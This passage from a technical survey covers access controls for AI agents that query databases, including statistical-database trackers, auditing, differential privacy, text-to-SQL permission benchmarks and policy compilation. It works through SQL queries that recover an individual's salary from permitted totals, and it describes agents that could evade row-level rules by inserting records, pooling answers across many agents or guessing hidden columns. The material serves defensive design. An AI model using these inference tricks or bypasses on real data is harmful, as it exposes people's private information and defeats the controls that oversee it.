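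Solver time may matter less for an agent than for a web page. At a few hundred milliseconds per check, 13 new queries would add several seconds to a task in which the agent already waits for a model to write each query. Refusals are likely to take longer. Zhang and colleagues found that solvers are good at proving that no violating pair of databases exists but often fail to find a pair when one does. A query that breaks the policy may therefore take the full five seconds, and because Blockaid does not cache refusals, the agent would wait again if it repeated the query. An agent that learns by trial and error would face these delays far more often than a tested application.

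Agents also run for longer than a web request, and a long trace makes the formula larger and slower to solve. An operator can safely discard old entries, because with fewer known answers the check must cover more possible databases, which can only make it stricter. The agent might then have to confirm again that Ben attends event 5. Keeping old entries is riskier, because the data may change. If the organiser removes Ben from event 5 at noon, his attendance record from the morning would still let the agent read a title that the organiser changes in the afternoon.

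False refusals would almost certainly become more common with an agent, because it keeps producing new queries, while the developers of a web application can rewrite an unsupported query once. Questions about data also often need `GROUP BY`. The closest test is in *FactGate* (Wu, 2026), which describes a gateway that limits how much data an agent can obtain during a task. The gateway accepts only queries in a restricted part of SQL. It accepted 22 of 40 queries (55 percent) that a language model wrote for new questions, and rejected others for features such as division, `OR` and left joins. It accepted none of the 22 query templates in the TPC-H benchmark. Blockaid supports a different part of SQL, which includes `OR` but not `GROUP BY`, so its acceptance rate could be higher or lower.

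An agent can still complete its task after a refusal. In Wu's 36 runs with an ordinary agent, the agent always completed its legitimate task after FactGate refused one of its requests. With Blockaid, an agent that is refused the title of event 5 could check Ben's attendance and try again, or put the check into the query with a join. The enforcer could also look up Ben's attendance itself, but Zhang and colleagues rejected this design, partly because they took an unchecked query as a sign of a bug in the application. That reason is less convincing for an agent, which may write a query and use it only once. Choosing the right lookups would still be difficult.

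An operator could use Ote to extract a policy from the web application that already serves the data, then enforce that policy on the agent. Ben's agent could then write its own queries but learn only what Ben could already find out through the application. Ote could not extract a policy from the agent itself, because a language model has no access checks in code to analyse.

Even a perfect policy of this kind does not limit how much of the permitted data an agent collects. Blockaid would let Ben's agent copy every event he attends when the task needs only one. Wu's FactGate addresses this by recording which facts a task has already obtained and refusing any query that would exceed a fixed budget. In a scripted sequence of 100 queries, row-level security answered all of them, while FactGate, with budgets set at 70 percent of the facts involved, stopped at the 37th. Updating the record took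 a median of 163 milliseconds when it already held about a million facts. This is fast for such a long history because FactGate only checks which facts are new, while Blockaid has to work out what the earlier answers imply. The complete process, however, took 22 to 144 times as long as running the query directly.

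## Statistical databases that answer only aggregate questions

A statistical database gives totals, counts and averages for groups but keeps each individual's data secret. For example, a company might let analysts see the total pay of any large group of staff but not any individual's salary. Blockaid cannot enforce this policy, because it allows a total only if the user may see every figure included in it. A simple alternative is to refuse totals over small groups, but a user can still work out one person's salary by combining several permitted totals.

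### Subtracting one total from another

Suppose that a staff database refuses any total over fewer than five people, and an agent sends two queries:

```
SELECT SUM(Salary) FROM Staff
WHERE Job = 'engineer'

SELECT SUM(Salary) FROM Staff
WHERE Job = 'engineer' AND City <> 'Oslo'
```

The first query sums the salaries of 40 engineers and returns 4,000,000. The second sums the salaries of the 39 engineers outside Oslo and returns 3,890,000. The database allows both queries, but the difference between the results, 110,000, is the salary of the only engineer in Oslo.

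In *Secure Databases*, Dobkin, Jones and Lipton (1979) concluded that access controls were the wrong tool for this problem because they "have no notion of a history of information already given out". Row-level security needs no such history because its answers do not depend on hidden rows, whereas every total in the staff database depends on hidden salaries.

### Trackers

In *The Tracker*, Denning, Denning and Schwartz (1979) studied databases with n records that answer a query only if it covers at least k records and at most n − k. The upper limit stops a user from subtracting the total for everyone but one person from the total for everyone. They showed that users can almost always get around both limits with a tracker, a condition that lets them calculate a refused answer from permitted ones.

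The Oslo queries use an individual tracker, which works for one person. A general tracker works for everyone in the database. It is any condition T that covers between 2k and n − 2k records. To find the total for a small group C, the user asks for four totals:

```
total(C) = total(C or T) + total(C or not T)
           − total(T) − total(not T)
```

The first two totals count the members of C twice and everyone else once, and subtracting the last two removes everyone once. The database permits all four, because adding fewer than k people to T, or to the people outside T, cannot take the group past the upper limit.

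Suppose the company has 100 employees and k is 5. The 40 engineers can serve as T, since any group of 10 to 90 people will do. Their salaries total 4,000,000, and those of the other 60 employees total 4,800,000. To find the salary of the head of finance, the agent asks for the total for the engineers and the head of finance, which is 4,180,000. It also asks for the total for the non-engineers and the head of finance, which is still 4,800,000 because the head is already among them. These two totals add to 8,980,000, and subtracting the 8,800,000 total for all employees leaves the head's salary, 180,000.

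A general tracker always exists if n is at least 4k and the records fall into at least 2k + 1 distinguishable classes. In this company, 11 different job titles would be enough. Finding a tracker is also easy. Denning and colleagues cite a calculation by Jan Schlörer that, if all values of each attribute are equally common, often more than 99 percent of the possible groups are trackers. A user could then find one by guessing.

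Raising k does not help much. No general tracker exists when k is above n/4, but a pair of conditions called a double tracker can work up to n/3, with at most seven queries. Setting k to 34 would rule out both kinds of tracker and limit the database to totals over 34 to 66 people, but the Oslo queries would still succeed because they cover 40 and 39. With k at 40, the agent could add the same 15 salespeople to both queries, bringing them to 55 and 54 people. At that setting, the company could not find the total pay of any department with fewer than 40 people, but a user could still find one engineer's salary.

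Denning and colleagues also doubted that limiting the conditions in queries would work, because users can rebuild complex conditions by adding and subtracting the answers to simple ones. A more promising idea was to divide the records into fixed blocks and answer only questions about whole blocks, so that users could never isolate one person. However, if the blocks were teams, nobody could ask for total pay by age or city. This protection also works only if the data do not change. If one person joins a team between two queries, the difference between the team's totals is the newcomer's salary.

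### Query auditing

An online auditor compares each new query with the earlier ones and refuses it if the combined answers would reveal a secret. Shmatikov's lecture slides, *Query Auditing*, distinguish this from offline auditing, which only detects a breach afterwards.

For totals of salaries, the auditor can use linear algebra. Each total is an equation, and the auditor refuses a query if the equations together would reveal anyone's salary. Once the agent has the total for the 40 engineers, the auditor refuses the total for the 39. If the agent asks in the opposite order, the auditor refuses the total for the 40 instead. No user can get more than 99 independent totals about 100 employees, because 100 independent equations would reveal every salary.

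Other kinds of data are much harder to audit. Suppose a column records whether each employee is on medical leave, with 1 for yes and 0 for no. If a count over five people returns 5, all of them are on leave. With many overlapping counts, the auditor has to work out whether any person has the same value in every combination of zeros and ones that fits the counts. Kleinberg, Papadimitriou and Raghavan proved in 2000 that this problem is coNP-complete, which means no known method solves it quickly in all cases. Auditing a mixture of totals and maximums is also NP-hard.

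An auditor can reveal private data by refusing to answer a query. Suppose the agent knows that five testers earn 500,000 in total, and asks for the highest salary among them. If the answer is 130,000, the auditor allows it because it does not show what any particular tester earns. If the answer is 100,000, the auditor refuses because all five must earn exactly that. The agent can then infer from the refusal that every tester earns 100,000. Kenthapadi's *Models and Algorithms for Data Privacy* describes this leak as a fundamental problem of online auditing.

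*Simulatable Auditing* (Kenthapadi, Mishra and Nissim, 2005) proposed a remedy. A simulatable auditor decides using only the earlier queries, their answers and the new query, never the answer to the new query. The user could therefore work out the decision without the auditor, so a refusal reveals nothing new. In the testers example, 100,000 is a possible answer, so the auditor refuses the query whatever the highest salary is. This closes the leak but adds false refusals, because the auditor also blocks the harmless answer of 130,000. The linear algebra test for totals is already simulatable, because it depends only on which people each total covers.

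These auditors prevent only exact disclosure, so they would allow answers showing that somebody earns between 109,000 and 111,000. Kenthapadi, Mishra and Nissim therefore also studied a stricter standard, which limits how much the answers may change what a user can reasonably believe about each value.

### How much noise is necessary

A database can return approximate answers instead of refusing queries. Dinur and Nissim proved in 2003 that small errors do not protect individuals' data if users can ask many questions. In their model, each of n people has a secret value of 0 or 1, and a user can ask how many people in any chosen group have the value 1. If every error is much smaller than √n, a user can feasibly compute almost all the secret values from the answers to somewhat more than n random queries.

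Suppose a guess at the whole database is wrong about many people. On a random group, its count usually differs from the true count by about the square root of the number of wrong entries. That exceeds the permitted error, so a few random queries are likely to rule the guess out. Any guess that fits all the answers must therefore be nearly correct, and linear programming can find one. In a company with 10,000 employees, √n is 100, or 2 percent of a group of 5,000. The theorem applies to any source of error, including rounding.

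The attack also works in practice. *Linear Program Reconstruction in Practice* (2018) describes how researchers used it against Diffix, a commercial system that adds noise to counts and suppresses low ones. In further experiments on a simulated system, a personal laptop solved every linear program in less than four seconds. *QueryCheetah* (Stevanoski, Cretu and de Montjoye, 2024) automates the search for sequences of aggregate queries that reveal a person's secret attribute, so attackers do not have to design the queries themselves. The program found stronger attacks than earlier methods, ran 18 times faster than the best previous automated search, and found ways around ad hoc defences.

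### Differential privacy

Differential privacy sets a limit on what all the answers together can reveal about any one person. According to Dwork, in *A Firm Foundation for Private Data Analysis*, it arose from a setting in which privacy remains difficult even when every problem of access control has been solved. A randomised method M is ε-differentially private if the following holds for every two databases D and D′ that differ in one person's record, and for every set S of possible outputs:

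```
P(M(D) ∈ S)  ≤  e^ε · P(M(D′) ∈ S)
```

The output is then almost as likely without a person's record as with it. A smaller ε gives more privacy. If ε is 0.5, adding or removing one person's record changes the probability of any result by a factor of at most e^0.5, about 1.65.

The Laplace mechanism achieves this by adding random noise to the true answer. The probability density of the noise z is proportional to e^(−|z|/b), where b is the noise scale:

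```
b = sensitivity / ε
```

The sensitivity is the largest change that one person can make to the true answer. One person can therefore shift the distribution of outputs by at most the sensitivity, which changes the probability density at any point by a factor of at most e^(sensitivity/b) = e^ε.

If the company caps each salary at 200,000 when computing totals, one person can change a total by at most 200,000. With ε at 0.5, the noise scale is 400,000. The average error is also 400,000, or about 10 percent of the total for the 40 engineers. If the agent subtracts the two noisy totals, the noise in the difference has a standard deviation of 800,000, which is far too large for the difference to reveal a salary of 110,000. For 40,000 engineers earning a total of 4 billion, the same average error would be only 0.01 percent.

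Privacy losses add up. *Private Queries with Sigma-Counting* (2025) explains that a combination of independent mechanisms with parameters ε₁, ε₂, … is differentially private with the sum of those parameters. Two totals released with ε = 0.5 each therefore have a combined parameter of 1.0. If 1.0 is the privacy budget, the largest combined parameter that the owner allows, the database must refuse every further query on these data. The agent can still analyse the noisy answers it already has without limit, because this causes no further privacy loss.

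The owner could instead split the budget across 100 totals, with ε = 0.01 for each. The noise scale would then be 20 million per total, five times the true total for the engineers. Under other forms of accounting, which allow a small probability of a larger privacy loss, more queries still make the answers less accurate, but the noise grows only roughly with the square root of the number of queries.

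An expressive query language makes a query's sensitivity harder to determine, because a join can copy one person's data into many rows. *DP4SQL* (2026), a paper on differentially private SQL, therefore limits the data in its university example, such as to at most six courses and two scholarships per student. It sets ε to 1 for each query, so the total ε for its four example queries could reach 4.

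### A budget over the whole history

The total salary of 39 engineers is harmless to a user who knows nothing else, but it reveals one person's salary to a user who already has the total for those 39 and one more. A rule that checks each query separately therefore cannot determine whether the total is safe to release. If a database allows flexible questions about groups, it can protect individuals only with a budget that covers the whole history of answers. The budget limits how much the user can learn, whether the agent writes SQL, writes Python or picks from a menu of totals. Fixed blocks and published tables need no running record only because their designer applied the budget in advance, when choosing which answers to release.

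Blockaid can safely discard old answers, because it uses them only to allow queries it would otherwise block. But a statistical database that discards them could release the second Oslo total, so it must keep its record for as long as the data are sensitive, even if the agent starts a new session every day.

A database can use its budget better if its designer can predict the questions. *LAPRAS* (2026) describes a system that answers a stream of queries. It sets aside part of its budget for predicted queries and divides the rest between unexpected queries and a safety reserve. It stops answering when the safety reserve falls below a minimum. An operator can save less in this way when they know less about how much generality an agent will need.

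*Dependency-Aware Privacy for Multi-turn LLM Agents* (2026) measured how smaller privacy budgets affect multi-turn agents. With one noise method, the average error in assigning risk classes rose from 0.6 to 15.7 percent as the budget ε fell from 5 to 0.1. The best method tested had an error of 3.6 percent at ε = 0.1, so careful design can recover much of the lost accuracy.

Without noise, a database has to release less detail. On June 4, 2026, the US Department of Commerce banned noise from the statistics of the Census Bureau and the Bureau of Economic Analysis. The department said its aim was accuracy. Its order makes coarser figures the preferred protection and allows agencies to suppress data as a last resort (reproduced in Desfontaines, *Banning noise will be a disaster for statistical data products*, 2026). APDU, an association of data users, reports in *Explaining Department Administrative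 Order “Disclosure Avoidance for Statistical Products”* (2026) that by August, the release of one-year data from the American Community Survey, a large yearly household survey, faced an indefinite delay. APDU also warns that figures for neighbourhoods and rural communities may disappear or become too coarse to use.

### When several accounts or agents pool their answers

If one account asks for the total salary of the 40 engineers and another asks for the total for the 39 outside Oslo, neither account's query history reveals anyone's salary. But the two users can subtract one total from the other and learn that the engineer in Oslo earns 110,000. *The future of statistical disclosure control* (2018) lists such collusion as one of the main weaknesses of systems that refuse queries, along with the burden of keeping track of earlier queries.

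To prevent collusion, an auditor has to treat everyone who might share answers as a single user. One person's questions can then cause refusals for everybody else, and a malicious user can ask questions that block useful ones.

Differential privacy weakens more gradually when users collude. If ten accounts each have a budget of 1, their pooled answers have a total parameter of at most 10. That guarantee is very weak, because it allows one person's data to change the probability of a given set of answers by a factor of up to e^10, or about 22,000. If the accounts instead share a budget of 1 equally, each has 0.1, and an account that used all of it on a single salary total would get an answer with a noise scale of 2 million.

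Separate budgets are especially risky with AI agents, because one person can start a hundred agents and combine their answers. If each agent has its own budget, the total privacy loss can be up to a hundred times the intended limit. An operator can prevent this by counting every agent's queries against the budget of the person it works for, but two people can still pool their answers. Only a single budget shared by everyone with access to the data keeps the total loss within the limit.

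## Agents that write SQL

A text-to-SQL system lets people question a database in ordinary language. A language model receives the question and a description of the tables and writes an SQL query, which the system runs. If some data are off limits, the operator can state the restriction in the prompt, have a second model check each query, or build the restriction into the decoder that turns the model's output into text, the tool that the model calls, or the database. The prompt and the second model rely on a model's judgment, while the decoder, the tool and the database can apply a rule mechanically.

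### Rules in the prompt

The simplest method is to put the user's permissions in the prompt and tell the model to refuse requests that exceed them. *Benchmarking Text-to-SQL under Role-Based Access Control* (Fei, Jiang and colleagues, 2026) measured how well this works. Role-based access control gives permissions to job roles, such as sales analyst, instead of to individuals.

Fei and colleagues took questions with known SQL answers from three benchmarks: Spider; BIRD, which has larger and messier databases; and LiveSQLBench, which also includes requests to change data. A language model generated plausible roles for the 53 databases, and people reviewed the roles. Fei and colleagues then paired each question with a random role and tested 13 models, repeating the test five times. The tested model should refuse if the question's reference query needs a column or operation that the role does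 not permit.

In the table, the first number is the percentage of all requests on which the model broke the rules, and the second is the percentage it wrongly refused.

| Model | Spider | BIRD | LiveSQLBench |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5 | 2.6 / 2.0 | 10.5 / 0.7 | 17.8 / 4.5 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 4.9 / 3.0 | 7.7 / 1.8 | 13.3 / 8.6 |
| DeepSeek V3.2, reasoning | 2.1 / 2.4 | 8.8 / 1.4 | 26.8 / 6.1 |
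| GPT-4o-mini | 17.0 / 10.4 | 29.7 / 5.1 | 25.4 / 12.2 |
| Snowflake-Arctic-R1-7B | 48.7 / 0.1 | 65.1 / 0.1 | 82.0 / 0.3 |

About half the requests on Spider, two thirds on BIRD and three quarters on LiveSQLBench should have been refused. Snowflake's specialized SQL model therefore scored about as badly as a model that ignored the permissions. Violations also became more common as questions required more joins. All these models date from 2025 or earlier, and current ones would probably do better.

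Fei and colleagues count any query as a violation if the model should have refused, so many of these violations are not leaks. In about 126 of GPT-5-mini's roughly 194 violations per run on BIRD, the question needed a forbidden column, but the model wrote a query using only permitted ones. Such a query reveals nothing forbidden, but the user may mistake its result for an answer. The other queries fail with an error if the database enforces the same rules. If the prompt is the only safeguard, the user gets the forbidden data.

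Leaving forbidden columns out of the table description reduced the violation rate of DeepSeek's coding variant on BIRD from 50 to 40 percent but raised GPT-5-mini's from 13 to 27 percent. GPT-5-mini more often answered with the columns it could see and also guessed the names of hidden columns.

Further training made models refuse too often. After Fei and colleagues trained Qwen2.5-14B on permitted and forbidden requests from Spider, its violation rate on Spider fell from 37 to 4 percent, but its rate of wrongful refusals rose from 0.5 to 20 percent. The share of permitted requests that it answered correctly fell from 69 to 50 percent.

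### A second model as checker

*Role-Conditioned Refusals* (Klisura, Khoury and colleagues, 2025) compared a single prompt with a two-step method, in which one model writes the query without considering permissions and a second model reads the query and the permissions and decides whether to run it. The study tested four small or medium-sized models on 153 Spider databases and 80 BIRD databases. Each database had four roles, ranging from one with full access to one limited to a few harmless tables.

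On BIRD, GPT-4o-mini with a single prompt refused 76 percent of the forbidden requests, and 35 percent of its refusals were wrong. With a checker, it refused 95 percent, and 22.5 percent of its refusals were wrong. On Spider, however, adding the checker to a version of DeepSeek-R1 lowered the share of forbidden requests it refused from 92 to 87 percent, while the share of its refusals that were wrong fell from 24 to 10 percent. Performance also dropped as policies grew longer. On a scale from 0 to 1 that combines both kinds of error, the two-step method with GPT-4o-mini scored 0.90 on short policies and 0.69 on long ones.

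Klisura and colleagues also trained models on Spider. The best, Mistral-7B, refused 93 percent of the forbidden requests on Spider, and 6 percent of its refusals were wrong. On BIRD, it refused 81 percent, and 44 percent of its refusals were wrong.

Using a separate model as the checker has one security advantage, because it does not have to read the web pages or documents that may have misled the first model. An attacker might still mislead it through a comment in the query. But these rules only concern which tables and columns a query uses, and an ordinary program can determine that by parsing the query. Klisura and colleagues used such a program to decide which requests the models should have refused. A model is therefore a poor choice for checking these rules, though it may be useful for rules that nobody can state precisely.

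### Mentioning a column and disclosing it

The rules in these two studies make a column either open or closed. But a query can use a column without showing its values:

```
SELECT Name, Salary FROM Staff
SELECT AVG(Salary) FROM Staff
```

Both queries mention the Salary column, but only the first lists what each person earns. A rule that checks only whether a query mentions Salary must either block both or allow both.

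Miyamoto, Xin and Yamana (2026), in *Policy-Conditioned Constrained Decoding for Column-Level Access Control in Text-to-SQL*, therefore let the data's owner choose among four settings for each column:

- **Public:** a query may use the column anywhere.
- **Condition only:** a query may use it to join tables or filter rows.
- **Aggregate only:** a query may use it only inside COUNT, SUM or AVG.
- **Hidden:** no query may use it.

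Their system, PCC-SQL, enforces these settings while the model writes. A language model produces text in small pieces called tokens. At each step, it gives every possible next token a score, and the decoder chooses a token based on the scores. PCC-SQL keeps track of where in the query the model is. At each point where a column name must follow, it sets the scores of forbidden columns to minus infinity, so the decoder cannot choose them. If Salary is aggregate only, the choices look like this:

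```
SELECT ...               Salary blocked
SELECT AVG( ...          Salary allowed
SELECT Name FROM Staff
WHERE ...                Salary blocked
```

This works because the text written so far determines how the query will use the next column. If no permitted column is available, PCC-SQL stops and refuses.

Miyamoto and colleagues tested it on 1,034 questions from Spider and 1,534 from BIRD, using a program to assign settings from column names and typical usage. The table gives percentages for Spider. "Permitted requests answered" is the share of requests with a permitted reference query for which the system wrote a compliant query. "Substitutes found" is the share of requests with a rule-breaking reference query for which the system wrote a compliant query, such as one that returns the average salary when the request was for individual salaries.

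| Method and model | Violations | Permitted requests answered | Substitutes found |
|---|---|---|---|
| Prompt, Claude Opus 4.5 | 20.4 | 84.5 | 6.9 |
| Prompt, Qwen 2.5 Coder 7B | 30.7 | 74.3 | 2.9 |
| Second model, Qwen 2.5 Coder 7B | 13.0 | 42.0 | 0.9 |
| Check and retry, Claude Opus 4.5 | 0.5 | 94.2 | 18.0 |
| PCC-SQL, Qwen 2.5 Coder 7B | 0.0 | 89.0 | 88.0 |
| PCC-SQL, DeepSeek Coder 6.7B | 0.0 | 68.1 | 58.3 |

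PCC-SQL had no violations with any model on either benchmark. However, a program that checks finished queries could also reach zero by blocking any query that still violates the rules after a few retries. PCC-SQL's advantage is that it finds substitutes for forbidden queries, though someone who asks what Ada earns may prefer a refusal to the company average.

A compliant query can also be wrong. With the larger Qwen 32B model, PCC-SQL wrote compliant queries for 83 percent of the permitted requests on Spider, but only 48 percent returned the correct result. On BIRD, the figures were 80 and 18 percent, the latter still the best result of any method with that model.

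In principle, PCC-SQL lets the model write any compliant query in the subset of SQL it covers, because its rules concern only the form of a query. The model can still fail to find a compliant query, since it cannot revise what it has already written. The subset leaves out common SQL features such as `CASE` and `UNION`. The method needs access to the model's scores, which Miyamoto and colleagues had only for open models. It does not protect the database if the agent can reach it by another route, such as a Python script.

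Even a compliant query can disclose a protected value:

```
SELECT AVG(Salary) FROM Staff
WHERE Name = 'Ada'
```

If Name is public and the company has one Ada, this returns her salary. Making salary condition-only is no safer, because an agent can narrow down each person's salary by listing everyone who earns over 100,000, then everyone over 110,000, and so on. Column settings control how a query uses a value, but they don't limit what the answers reveal about one person.

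### Fixed tools or free SQL

An operator can avoid these problems by not letting the agent write SQL at all, as Microsoft's *The Polyglot tax* (2026), a series on SQL Server, recommends. Microsoft argues that models are most likely to make subtle errors in complex queries, which are the ones users most want help with. Instead, people write and review stored procedures, which are queries saved in the database with blanks for values such as a customer number. The agent's account can run these procedures but has no direct access to the tables, and row-level security still applies when the procedures run. Oracle, however, considers predefined functions too limiting for analysis.

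How much generality this costs depends on the questions. Suppose an online shop's sales analyst has an agent with five tools. They return the contents of an order (`order`), a customer's orders (`customer_orders`), a product's monthly sales (`product_sales`), a month's best sellers (`top_products`) and a month's returned items by product (`returns`). In one month, the analyst asks twelve questions:

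| Question | Can the five tools answer it? |
|---|---|
| What did order 881 contain? | Yes, with `order` |
| Has customer 40 bought a kettle before? | Yes, with `customer_orders` |
| How have kettle sales changed this year? | Yes, with `product_sales` |
| Which ten products sold best in May? | Yes, with `top_products` |
| Which products came back most often in May? | Yes, with `returns` |
| How many kettles came back in May per 100 sold? | Yes, with `returns` and `product_sales` |
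| Which of May's ten best sellers sold less than in April? | Yes, with eleven calls |
| Which customers ordered in April but not in May? | No |
| What is the average order worth in each country? | No |
| What do people buy together with kettles? | No |
| Do customers who return something order again? | No |
| Did free delivery above €50 lead to more orders of that size? | No |

The tools can answer seven of the twelve questions, though some of these require combining tools. The other five require comparing many customers or orders, which no tool does. An agent with SQL could answer each with a query or two, and row-level security could still limit it to the analyst's own region. The developer could add more tools, but would have to guess next month's questions. Microsoft also offers seven generic tools that read, total and change records by building SQL from structured arguments. They cover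 more questions because they amount to a small query language.

Fixed tools can also reveal more than their designer intended. If the shop numbers its orders in sequence and `order` accepts any number, the agent can fetch every order and use them to answer most of the remaining questions itself. Fetching 50,000 orders takes 50,000 calls, which is too slow for everyday analysis but fast enough for theft. A fixed tool still needs a rule about which rows it may return.

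The choice between typed tool calls and SQL may make little difference to security if the same authorization rule applies to both. *VirtualSet* (Zhang, 2026) tested approvals to act on records that a query had selected, in 40 scenarios where the data or their structure changed before the action. The same authorization layer kept 22 approvals and blocked 18, whether the program had selected the records with typed tool calls or with SQL.

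A database rule protects nothing if the agent connects with an account that is exempt from it.

### Removing protected fields from a tool's answer

A permitted tool may return a record with some protected fields. *Subjects, Not Authors* (Lee and Lee, 2026) studies this problem in trade between companies. Its example is a certificate of origin, which lists a product's code and country along with the names of the exporter, the producer and the recipient. A contract lets another company's agent read the certificate but requires the sender to remove the names.

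Lee and Lee compared three ways to carry out this duty. The first puts it in the agent's prompt, and the second hides tools that the agent may not use. The third compiles the contract into a constraint that a gateway applies to the tool's output before the model receives it. They tested 105 cases with protected names in various fields, lists and nested records. The names reached the model in all 105 cases with the prompt and with hidden tools, and in none with the compiled constraint. The constraint removed no permitted fields and took about 19 microseconds.

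No model took part in this test. The prompted result was inevitable, because an instruction to a model does not change what a tool returns. The gateway test was more informative, though Lee and Lee had designed the gateway for cases of this kind. They also tried harder cases, in which a name appeared in free text or a scanned attachment, or could be inferred from permitted fields. The name got through in all seven of the harder cases where they could detect a leak automatically. Trade documents often contain free-text remarks, and nobody has measured how often those remarks include protected names.

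Lee and Lee also tested nine model configurations, including versions of Claude and GPT, over 1,317 counted calls. With the duty in the prompt, every model received the protected names. Three configurations never repeated them, even when requests were designed to extract them, while one small open model repeated them in 47 of 60 extraction attempts. With the compiled constraint, none of the models received the names, and they completed as many legitimate tasks as before. In a separate study of prompted models, 27 of 52 leaks occurred in refusals that quoted the protected value.

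### Privacy norms as SQL views

Laws and company policies rarely name tables and columns. *PIMENTO* (Sadia, Chen and Roy Chowdhury, 2026) describes a system that translates written privacy norms into authorization views. The system follows contextual integrity, a theory in which privacy depends on whether information flows suit their context. For example, a hospital may let an attending physician disclose a patient's diagnosis to a resident for treatment if the physician supervises the resident and the resident is on the patient's care team.

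A language model translates this norm into several SQL views, which select the attending physicians, the residents, the patients, the diagnoses, and the cases that meet the conditions on supervision and care teams. The system then runs fixed checks on the views. It reports clauses that the model failed to translate, and looks for contradictory norms and for permitted data that would reveal prohibited data. For example, if the policy prohibits disclosing a patient's HIV status and a diagnosis would reveal it, the system withholds the diagnosis too.

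When the resident asks a question, a model translates it into SQL. PIMENTO then fills in who is asking, who is disclosing and for what purpose. It determines which data the norms permit, without using a model at this stage, and runs the query on only those data.

Sadia and colleagues tested the system on 450 requests under policies based on US health, consumer and children's privacy laws. The table shows how often each system's answers revealed prohibited information. All the systems used the model GPT-5.6-Luna.

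| Method | Health | Consumer | Children |
|---|---|---|---|
| No policy | 88.7% | 85.2% | 100% |
| Policy in the prompt | 18.0% | 52.3% | 44.3% |
| Another model filters the text first | 6.7% | 38.9% | 7.4% |
| PIMENTO | 0.0% | 2.1% | 1.3% |
| PIMENTO with hand-checked views | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |

All of PIMENTO's leaks came from errors in translating the policies. These errors were common. On a scale from 0 to 100 that combines missing and incorrect parts, the views scored 68 for the health policy, 71 for the consumer policy and 90 for the children's policy. The model omitted parts more often than it added incorrect ones. If it omits a permission, the system withholds data that it should release, which the comparison of leaks does not count. Averages can also be misleading, as they are under row-level security.

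PIMENTO can also answer counting questions about all the data by adding noise for differential privacy. Correct queries for the same question may need different amounts of noise, because one person can affect more rows in one join than in another. PIMENTO chose a correct query that needed the least noise for up to 75 percent of the test questions with several correct queries, compared with at most 60 percent for the other methods.

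### Who may change the rules

A restriction on an agent holds only while the agent cannot change it. *Protection in Operating Systems* (Harrison, Ruzzo and Ullman, 1976) models how permissions spread, using a table with a row for each subject, such as a running program, and a column for each object, such as a file. Each cell lists the subject's rights to the object. Commands can add or delete rights and create or destroy subjects and objects, and they may require certain rights to be present first. For example, one command lets the owner of a file give another program the right to read it.

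The safety question is whether any sequence of commands could give a subject a right it should not have. Harrison and colleagues proved that no algorithm can answer this for every system. The commands are simple, but they can create new subjects without limit, so the table can serve as a computer's memory. Someone could write commands that simulate any program and grant a particular right only when the program finishes. An algorithm that always answered the safety question would therefore also decide whether any given program finishes, which Turing proved impossible.

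A particular system may still be provably safe. Harrison and colleagues also gave an algorithm for checking safety in systems where each command performs only one operation, though they called such systems "not terribly realistic". Even creating a file and recording its owner takes two operations. Tripunitara and Li later corrected an error in a proof about how hard these simpler systems are to check, in *The Foundational work of Harrison-Ruzzo-Ullman Revisited*.

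The question is easy to answer if the agent has no command that changes permissions, directly or indirectly. Its rights are then those that others have granted, and a program can look them up. Lee and Lee make this a design rule, under which an agent is always subject to policy and cannot set it. The agent may draft a policy, but only a person can approve it, and the system that publishes policies accepts only the exact text that the person approved.

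In SQL, this means that the agent's account must not own tables, grant permissions or create policies. But some ordinary data also control access. The calendar's row-level policy lets Ben see the events for which he has an attendance record. If his agent is allowed to add attendance records, it can add one for event 6 and read "Surprise party for Ben" without changing the policy.

Lee and Lee measured a similar effect. They made 90 separate changes to a sample agreement and its data labels, and compared the system's decisions on 344,512 possible requests before and after each change. Six of the changes only moved a field to a less sensitive class, and all six made the system permit requests it had previously refused. A checker that compared only the policy's text missed all six. A broader checker, which also looked at the labels and treated any possible loosening as suspicious, caught all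 75 changes that affected permissions or duties, but also flagged the 15 harmless ones.

An agent that only drafts policies can still influence them, because a busy reviewer may approve a harmful draft. Lee and Lee estimate that a central office would need one reviewer for every 20 to 138 participating companies, depending on how many drafts arrive. They did not measure how often reviewers would notice a harmful change.

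## TACIT: agents that act by writing type-checked code

An agent that writes SQL works with one database, but many tasks also involve files, email and web services. Developers increasingly let agents handle such tasks by writing short programs that call several tools, instead of requesting one tool at a time. TACIT, a system from Martin Odersky's group at the Swiss university EPFL, lets agents write these programs in a general programming language and tries to prove limits on what each program can do. A compiler checks each program before it runs and rejects, for example, one that would copy a confidential document to an ordinary file.

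### Why agents write code

The result of each ordinary tool call passes through the model. Anthropic's *Code execution with MCP* (November 2025) gives the example of an agent that copies a sales meeting transcript from Google Drive into a customer record. The model must read the transcript and write it out again, which can take an extra 50,000 tokens for a two-hour meeting. A program can pass the text directly from one tool to the other. An agent that writes code can also load only the tool descriptions it needs, which cuts token use from 150,000 to 2,000 in Anthropic's example.

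Savings in actual tests are smaller. According to Anthropic's *Programmatic tool calling*, calling tools from code reduced billed input tokens by about 38 percent on a project-management benchmark with 75 tools, with no change in accuracy. On web search benchmarks, it improved results by an average of 11 percent and used 24 percent fewer input tokens. But on τ²-bench, a customer service simulation where each turn needs only one or two calls, scores stayed the same and costs rose by about 8 percent. OpenAI's *The builder’s guide to GPT‑5.6* (2026) quotes a financial research company that got equally good answers with 21 percent fewer input tokens.

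*The Bitter Lesson of Tool Calling* (Patel, Sen et al., 2026) compared writing code with making ordinary tool calls on 309 tasks with 14 models. Code was at least as accurate for 11 of the models, and the accuracy of GPT-5.6 Sol rose from 72 to 83 percent. Three older OpenAI models lost 20 to 27 percentage points because they wrote line breaks in a form that Python could not run. Code helped most when a task needed many calls. When asked to make 100 separate calls at once, Claude Sonnet 5 always left some out, but it made all of them when it could write a program. The tools only returned their own arguments, so the study measured whether models made the right calls, not whether they finished real tasks.

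The drawback is that a program can take many actions before anybody sees a result. OpenAI's *Programmatic Tool Calling* describes an isolated environment where programs have no direct network access and can affect other systems only through permitted tools. Even so, OpenAI advises developers to use ordinary tool calls for changes to data and for actions that need approval, to "preserve a clear authorization boundary".

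Isolation also does not control how a program combines permitted actions. Suppose an agent is allowed to read a private file and send text to the company that hosts its model. A sandbox permits both actions, so the program can leak the file by sending its contents to that company. TACIT is designed to catch this kind of leak.

### Object capabilities and capture sets

In most programming languages, any part of a program can open any file whose name it knows. An object capability is an unforgeable program value that grants a particular kind of access. If the value `out` stands for the file `notes.txt`, code that holds `out` can write to the file, while code without it cannot reach the file at all, even if it knows the name. The approach dates from the 1960s, and designers have since used it in operating systems, hardware and programming languages.

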